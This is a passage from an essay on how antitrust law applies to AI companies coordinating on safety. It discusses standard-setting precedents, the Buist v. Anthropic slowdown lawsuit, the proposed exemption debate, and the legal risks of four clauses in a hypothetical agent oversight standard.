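Courts judge most agreements between competitors by their effects, under the rule of reason. The plaintiff has to show that the firms have market power and that the agreement harms competition, for example by raising prices or lowering quality. The firms can answer that it also helps customers, perhaps by making products work together. The plaintiff can reply that a less restrictive agreement would have helped customers just as much. A few kinds of agreement, such as those to fix prices or divide up customers, are illegal without this analysis, even if they have benefits.

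Courts haven't always treated standards leniently. Hovenkamp (2026), in *Antitrust and AI's Threat to Humanity*, traces the Supreme Court's approval of standard setting by competitors to a 1925 case about maple flooring, but by the 1960s the Court had become extremely suspicious of private safety standards. In one case, a manufacturer alleged that a trade association had unfairly denied its gas burners a seal of approval, and that gas companies then refused to supply gas for them. The Court let the claim proceed without requiring the manufacturer to show wider harm to the public. Today, genuine standard setting falls under the rule of reason. A body that covers a whole industry usually has market power, so disputes tend to be about its conduct.

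A common stop message gives customers something that no provider could offer alone. Each provider gives up its own message format but can still compete on price, speed and the quality of its models. A joint slowdown gives customers no new product and limits the competition that would otherwise improve existing ones.

An agreement between rivals can break competition law even if they have good intentions. In 1978 the Supreme Court considered the National Society of Professional Engineers' ban on competitive bidding by its members. The society argued that low bids would lead to dangerous buildings. The Court rejected this defence because a firm can't justify restraining competition by arguing that competition itself is harmful. Companies defending an AI slowdown would need to make a very similar argument.

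Hovenkamp, a leading American antitrust scholar, considers a bare agreement to restrain innovation unlikely to work, and doubts that profit-seeking competitors would choose the right pace. But he concedes that a powerful enough threat might overcome the courts' resistance. A 1969 case suggests that restraint is not always safe. The Justice Department accused American carmakers of agreeing not to compete in developing and installing pollution controls. The carmakers settled, so no court decided whether the accusation was true. If it was, their agreement held back a technology that protected public health.

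### Eliason, Allied Tube and Hydrolevel

The National Sanitation Foundation, a private body, set standards for commercial refrigerators and rejected a design by the manufacturer Eliason, which sued and lost. In 1980 a federal appeals court held that a rejected company had to show either that the body had discriminated in favour of its competitors or that the conduct as a whole was "manifestly anticompetitive and unreasonable". Hovenkamp stresses that manufacturers had objectively reasonable requirements to follow before selling a product, and that states could use the same criteria in their own safety rules.

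The safeguard here is objective criteria, published in advance and applied to everyone. "Halts the agent within five seconds of a stop message" would be objective, since a provider can measure its own platform before applying. "Shows adequate commitment to safety" would not, because a rejected provider couldn't tell why it had failed or whether a competitor had really passed.

*Allied Tube* concerned an electrical code that the National Fire Protection Association writes and many states and cities adopt as law. In 1980 the association's members voted on whether to approve plastic conduit, the pipe that protects wiring inside walls. Steel-conduit makers recruited 230 people to join the association, attend the meeting and vote no. The proposal failed by 394 votes to 390. A jury awarded a plastic-conduit maker $3.8 million in damages, before trebling, and in 1988 the Supreme Court ruled in that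 company's favour.

The steel makers had not broken any of the association's rules. They argued that because governments copied the code, they had simply been lobbying, which the law protects. The Court disagreed because people with a financial stake had used a private body's power to decide. AI providers should expect courts to reject the same defense if a legislature later adopts their oversight standard.

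**Open participation** is a safeguard, but it also made the abuse in *Allied Tube* possible, because anyone could pay to join and vote. A standards body therefore also has to limit how many votes one commercial interest can cast. The Agentic AI Foundation has the opposite weakness, because it has few seats and companies that sell their own models appoint most of its board. Requiring **recorded reasons** for votes would help with both problems. The 230 people recruited to vote in *Allied Tube* would have had trouble writing a technical case against plastic pipe, and a board that rejected a stop message would have to give a reason that outsiders could check.

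The problem in *Hydrolevel* was how a standard was interpreted, not the standard itself. Hydrolevel made a device that shut off a boiler's fuel when the water ran low. An executive at a competitor served on the American Society of Mechanical Engineers committee that interpreted the society's boiler code. The executive and the committee's chair helped draft a question to the society about devices like Hydrolevel's. The chair then drafted the answer, which suggested that the devices were unsafe, and the society sent it out under its own name. The competitor's salespeople showed it to customers.

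The Supreme Court held the society liable in 1982, although it had neither approved the scheme nor gained from it. The Court reasoned that liability would encourage standards bodies to watch the people who act in their name. The natural safeguard is an appeal to people with no stake in the result. Suppose provider B's platform halts agents in five seconds but takes another second to confirm the halt. If an engineer from provider A alone decides whether the platform conforms, provider B has good reason to distrust the answer, even if it is correct.

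### Laws that protect standards work

The Standards Development Organization Advancement Act of 2004 guarantees that courts will apply the rule of reason to a qualifying body's standards work. If the body notifies the Justice Department and the Federal Trade Commission (FTC), its liability for work covered by the notice is limited to actual damages instead of triple damages. To qualify, its standards process must include openness, a balance of interests, due process, an appeals process and consensus.

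The act has no expiry date, but its protection is narrow. It covers the organisation but not the companies that take part, so it might have reduced the damages the engineering society owed in *Hydrolevel* but wouldn't have helped the steel makers. It also excludes price fixing, dividing up markets and exchanging commercial information that the standard doesn't require. A consortium whose members buy their board seats may struggle to show a balance of interests.

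The Cybersecurity Information Sharing Act of 2015 goes further, but covers a narrower range of activity. It exempts companies from antitrust law when they exchange cyber-threat indicators or defensive measures for a cybersecurity purpose. Provider A could warn provider B that someone is using a stolen agent credential from a particular network address. The act doesn't protect boycotts or the exchange of prices, customer lists or future competitive plans. It also wouldn't obviously cover sharing information about the firm's duplicate orders, which came from a programming mistake.

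This law lapsed on 1 October 2025, but Congress revived it that November and later extended it to 30 September 2026. A company that wants to rely on it has to check whether Congress has renewed it again. Without the exemption, companies lose a clear defence if somebody sues, though sharing threat information isn't automatically illegal. The Justice Department and the FTC said in 2014 that properly designed sharing was unlikely to raise antitrust concerns.

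In July 2026, Senators Jim Banks, a Republican, and Adam Schiff, a Democrat, proposed a limited antitrust exemption for AI companies that warn one another about threats, according to *AI Safety Regulation Pushed by OpenAI and Anthropic* (Mills, 2026). As described, the exemption would cover these warnings but not an agreement to slow down.

The European Commission's 2023 guidelines on cooperation between competitors set out four conditions under which a standard will normally raise no concern:

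- anyone in the affected market can take part in writing it;
- the procedure is transparent;
- nobody is obliged to comply with it;
- everyone can get access to it on fair, reasonable and non-discriminatory terms.

An agreement that fails one of these conditions isn't necessarily illegal, but the companies have to assess its effects themselves. The guidelines are much harsher on manufacturers who set a standard and then press others not to sell noncompliant products.

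A European case about diesel cars clearly shows the difference between agreeing on a specification and agreeing to limit competition. Daimler, BMW and the Volkswagen group met to discuss AdBlue, a liquid that removes pollutants from exhaust. In 2021 the European Commission found that they had also agreed not to clean emissions better than the law required, and fined BMW and Volkswagen €875 million. Daimler escaped a fine because it had reported the others. But the Commission told the companies it did not object to some of their other cooperation, including a standard filler neck for the AdBlue tank. The same engineers had made both kinds of agreement, sometimes about the same part of the car.

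### Buist v. Anthropic

On 12 September 2026, Anthropic's chief executive, Dario Amodei, published an essay calling for industry-wide cooperation to slow the improvement of AI models. Sam Altman of OpenAI, Elon Musk of SpaceXAI and Demis Hassabis of Google DeepMind publicly agreed the same day. Six days later, four AI subscribers sued the companies in federal court in California on behalf of a proposed nationwide class.

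The case, *Buist v. Anthropic*, rests on one claim under Section 1 of the Sherman Act. Its theory of harm is unusual, as Levine (2026) explains in *Anthropic, OpenAI, SpaceXAI and Google Accused of Agreeing to Slow AI Progress*. Antitrust plaintiffs normally point to higher prices, but these plaintiffs argue that subscribers get less for their money because they pay the same monthly price for models that improve more slowly than they would under competition.

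The plaintiffs object to the companies agreeing with one another. They don't object to a company slowing down on its own, or to companies asking Congress for regulation or an exemption, as Huamani (2026) reports in *Lawsuit says Anthropic, OpenAI, SpaceXAI and Google made illegal agreement*. The complaint also doesn't accuse the companies of inventing the danger.

The plaintiffs' evidence is almost entirely public. Stan (2026), in *The AI slowdown pact is now a Sherman Act lawsuit*, found no internal documents, confidential witnesses or minutes in the filing. The plaintiffs treat Amodei's essay as an offer and the other executives' posts as acceptance. Amodei had written that the government would need to issue "a narrow waiver for certain kinds of safety conversations", which the plaintiffs present as proof that the companies knew they were coordinating. Altman then said that OpenAI didn't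 need to wait for an exemption, which they present as proof that the companies intended to go ahead anyway.

The companies can reply that saying in public that everyone should slow down isn't a promise to do it, and that asking for a waiver could equally suggest that no agreement would start without one. The plaintiffs also concede that the alleged agreement had not yet affected any shipped product. But they allege that a working group of company representatives had been meeting regularly since July. Those discussions may matter more than the posts.

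By 3 October, the plaintiffs had served all four companies, which had until 14 or 15 October to respond. The court had not certified a class by then. The first case conference is set for 23 December 2026, so even if the claim survives, a ruling on whether there was an illegal agreement is probably a long way off.

The lawsuit doesn't challenge technical standards, but the same providers would have to meet to write an oversight interface. If executives compare release dates over lunch at a meeting where engineers are working on the stop message, a plaintiff will ask for records of both discussions. Keeping a written agenda and minutes and banning discussion of release plans would take little effort.

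### The argument over an exemption

The companies seem to have asked for more than Amodei's narrow waiver. Law360's *Trump Admin Calls AI Giants' Exemption Bid 'Moat-Digging'* reports that AI companies asked both Congress and federal regulators for a broad exemption that would let them coordinate a slowdown. The administration's term "moat-digging" means trying to keep competitors out. FTC chair Andrew Ferguson also questioned the sincerity of companies that want more safety regulation while seeking permission to agree on development limits, according to Law360's *FTC Chair Wary Of AI's Dual Push For Regs, Antitrust Shield*. Republican senator Josh Hawley told a hearing that there was "no world" in which he would agree to an exemption.

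Critics outside government were just as harsh. Hanley and Rao (2026) call the request a ruse in *How to Govern the Pacing of the AI Frontier*. Ferguson's suspicion isn't entirely fair, because a company could sincerely want regulation and also want to cooperate until it arrives. But an exemption would protect sincere and insincere companies equally.

Antitrust lawyers have mostly asked whether the companies need an exemption at all. In *4 Paths To AI Safety Coordination Amid Antitrust Debate*, Miller argues that existing routes, which offer different degrees of protection and oversight, give the companies more room for collective safety work than the debate suggests.

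On 17 November, the U.S. Chamber of Commerce's *AI & Antitrust* (2026) published answers from unnamed specialists to a question about rivals who agree to slow or coordinate the release of new capabilities. Most opposed an antitrust exemption but wanted guidance from the agencies. Several mentioned business review letters, in which the Justice Department tells companies whether it currently intends to challenge a plan they have described. One specialist wanted an exemption or guidance for any explicit coordination, fearing a slippery slope without it.

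The specialists disagreed most sharply over whether safety can count in the companies' favour. One argued that officials shouldn't offset harm to competition with benefits of a different kind, partly because the *Professional Engineers* decision may forbid it. The same specialist preferred guidance to a statute because agencies can amend guidance more easily when technology changes. Another warned that industries have long used safety as a cover for anticompetitive standards. The Chamber's article quotes only seven answers, so it is better evidence of the arguments than of how common each view is.

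Guidance from the US Justice Department would suit an oversight interface well, because providers could submit the draft specification, voting rules and fees and get an answer before building anything. But a favourable letter wouldn't bind private plaintiffs such as the subscribers in *Buist*, and the department can change its position, as it did in 2020 when it publicly revised a letter it had given the IEEE five years earlier.

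### Four clauses in an agreement

Suppose several providers bring a draft agreement to a standards body, with four clauses.

| Clause | Risk | What it mostly depends on |
|---|---|---|
| A common log format | Lower | Whether rivals also see one another's logs |
| A certification fee | Lower | Whether small providers can afford it |
| A shared list of barred agents | Higher | Whether each member decides for itself |
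| No shipping of uncertified features | Highest | Whether rivals or the law impose it |

**The log format** resembles the AdBlue filler neck. It lets the firm's security officer search both agents' records with one query and leaves the providers free to compete. The legal risk rises if the providers also pool the records, which could reveal customers, prices and unreleased features. The format itself could also be unfair, for example if it requires a field that only one provider's platform can fill in, or a method on which one provider secretly holds a patent.

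**A certification fee** is normal because the laboratory has to be paid. But a flat fee can exclude small companies even if no rule excludes them. If each test costs $20,000 and a provider releases four models a year, it pays $80,000. That is 0.008% of revenue for a company with $1 billion in sales and 8% for one with $1 million. The body could charge small companies less, and let a provider rerun automated tests itself when only the model has changed. It should also charge members and non-members the same for the same test. The providers mustn't agree on how much of the fee to pass on to customers, because that would come close to fixing prices.

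A shared list of barred agents is a modern version of the gas companies' refusal to supply gas for unapproved burners. If the members all agree to refuse every agent on the list, they have organised a boycott, and a competitor's agent could be listed by mistake or on purpose. They can reduce the risk by sharing evidence instead of verdicts. A member might report that agent 4417 used a stolen login at 14:05, and each member would then decide what to do. Google handled Symantec's certificates in roughly this way, passing its findings to other browser makers to verify. The drawback of separate decisions is that an agent blocked on one platform can keep working on another until somebody there reads the report. An agent's owner should also be able to see the evidence and appeal.

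**The agreement not to ship uncertified features** looks like the strongest safety measure of the four and is the hardest to defend. If certification took six months, no member would lose customers to another by waiting, so none would have much reason to demand a faster test. Members could also delay a feature that only one of them was ready to sell. This is close to what the Justice Department accused the carmakers of doing.

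Members can sometimes legally refuse a product. Hovenkamp thinks participants in a proper standards process may agree not to deploy a product the process has identified as unsafe. A feature that failed a published test for obeying stop messages might qualify. But a refusal of all "uncertified" features would also cover those nobody has tested yet.

A safer clause would reserve the certification mark for features that pass, as FIDO certification does for authenticators, and let members sell other features without it. This weakens the interface where the five providers in the earlier example most needed a check on uncertified features, because a provider that gains nothing from certification can skip it. Competition law makes it risky for the providers to agree among themselves to require certification. A bank acting alone can still refuse to buy uncertified agents, and a legislature can require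 certification of every provider.
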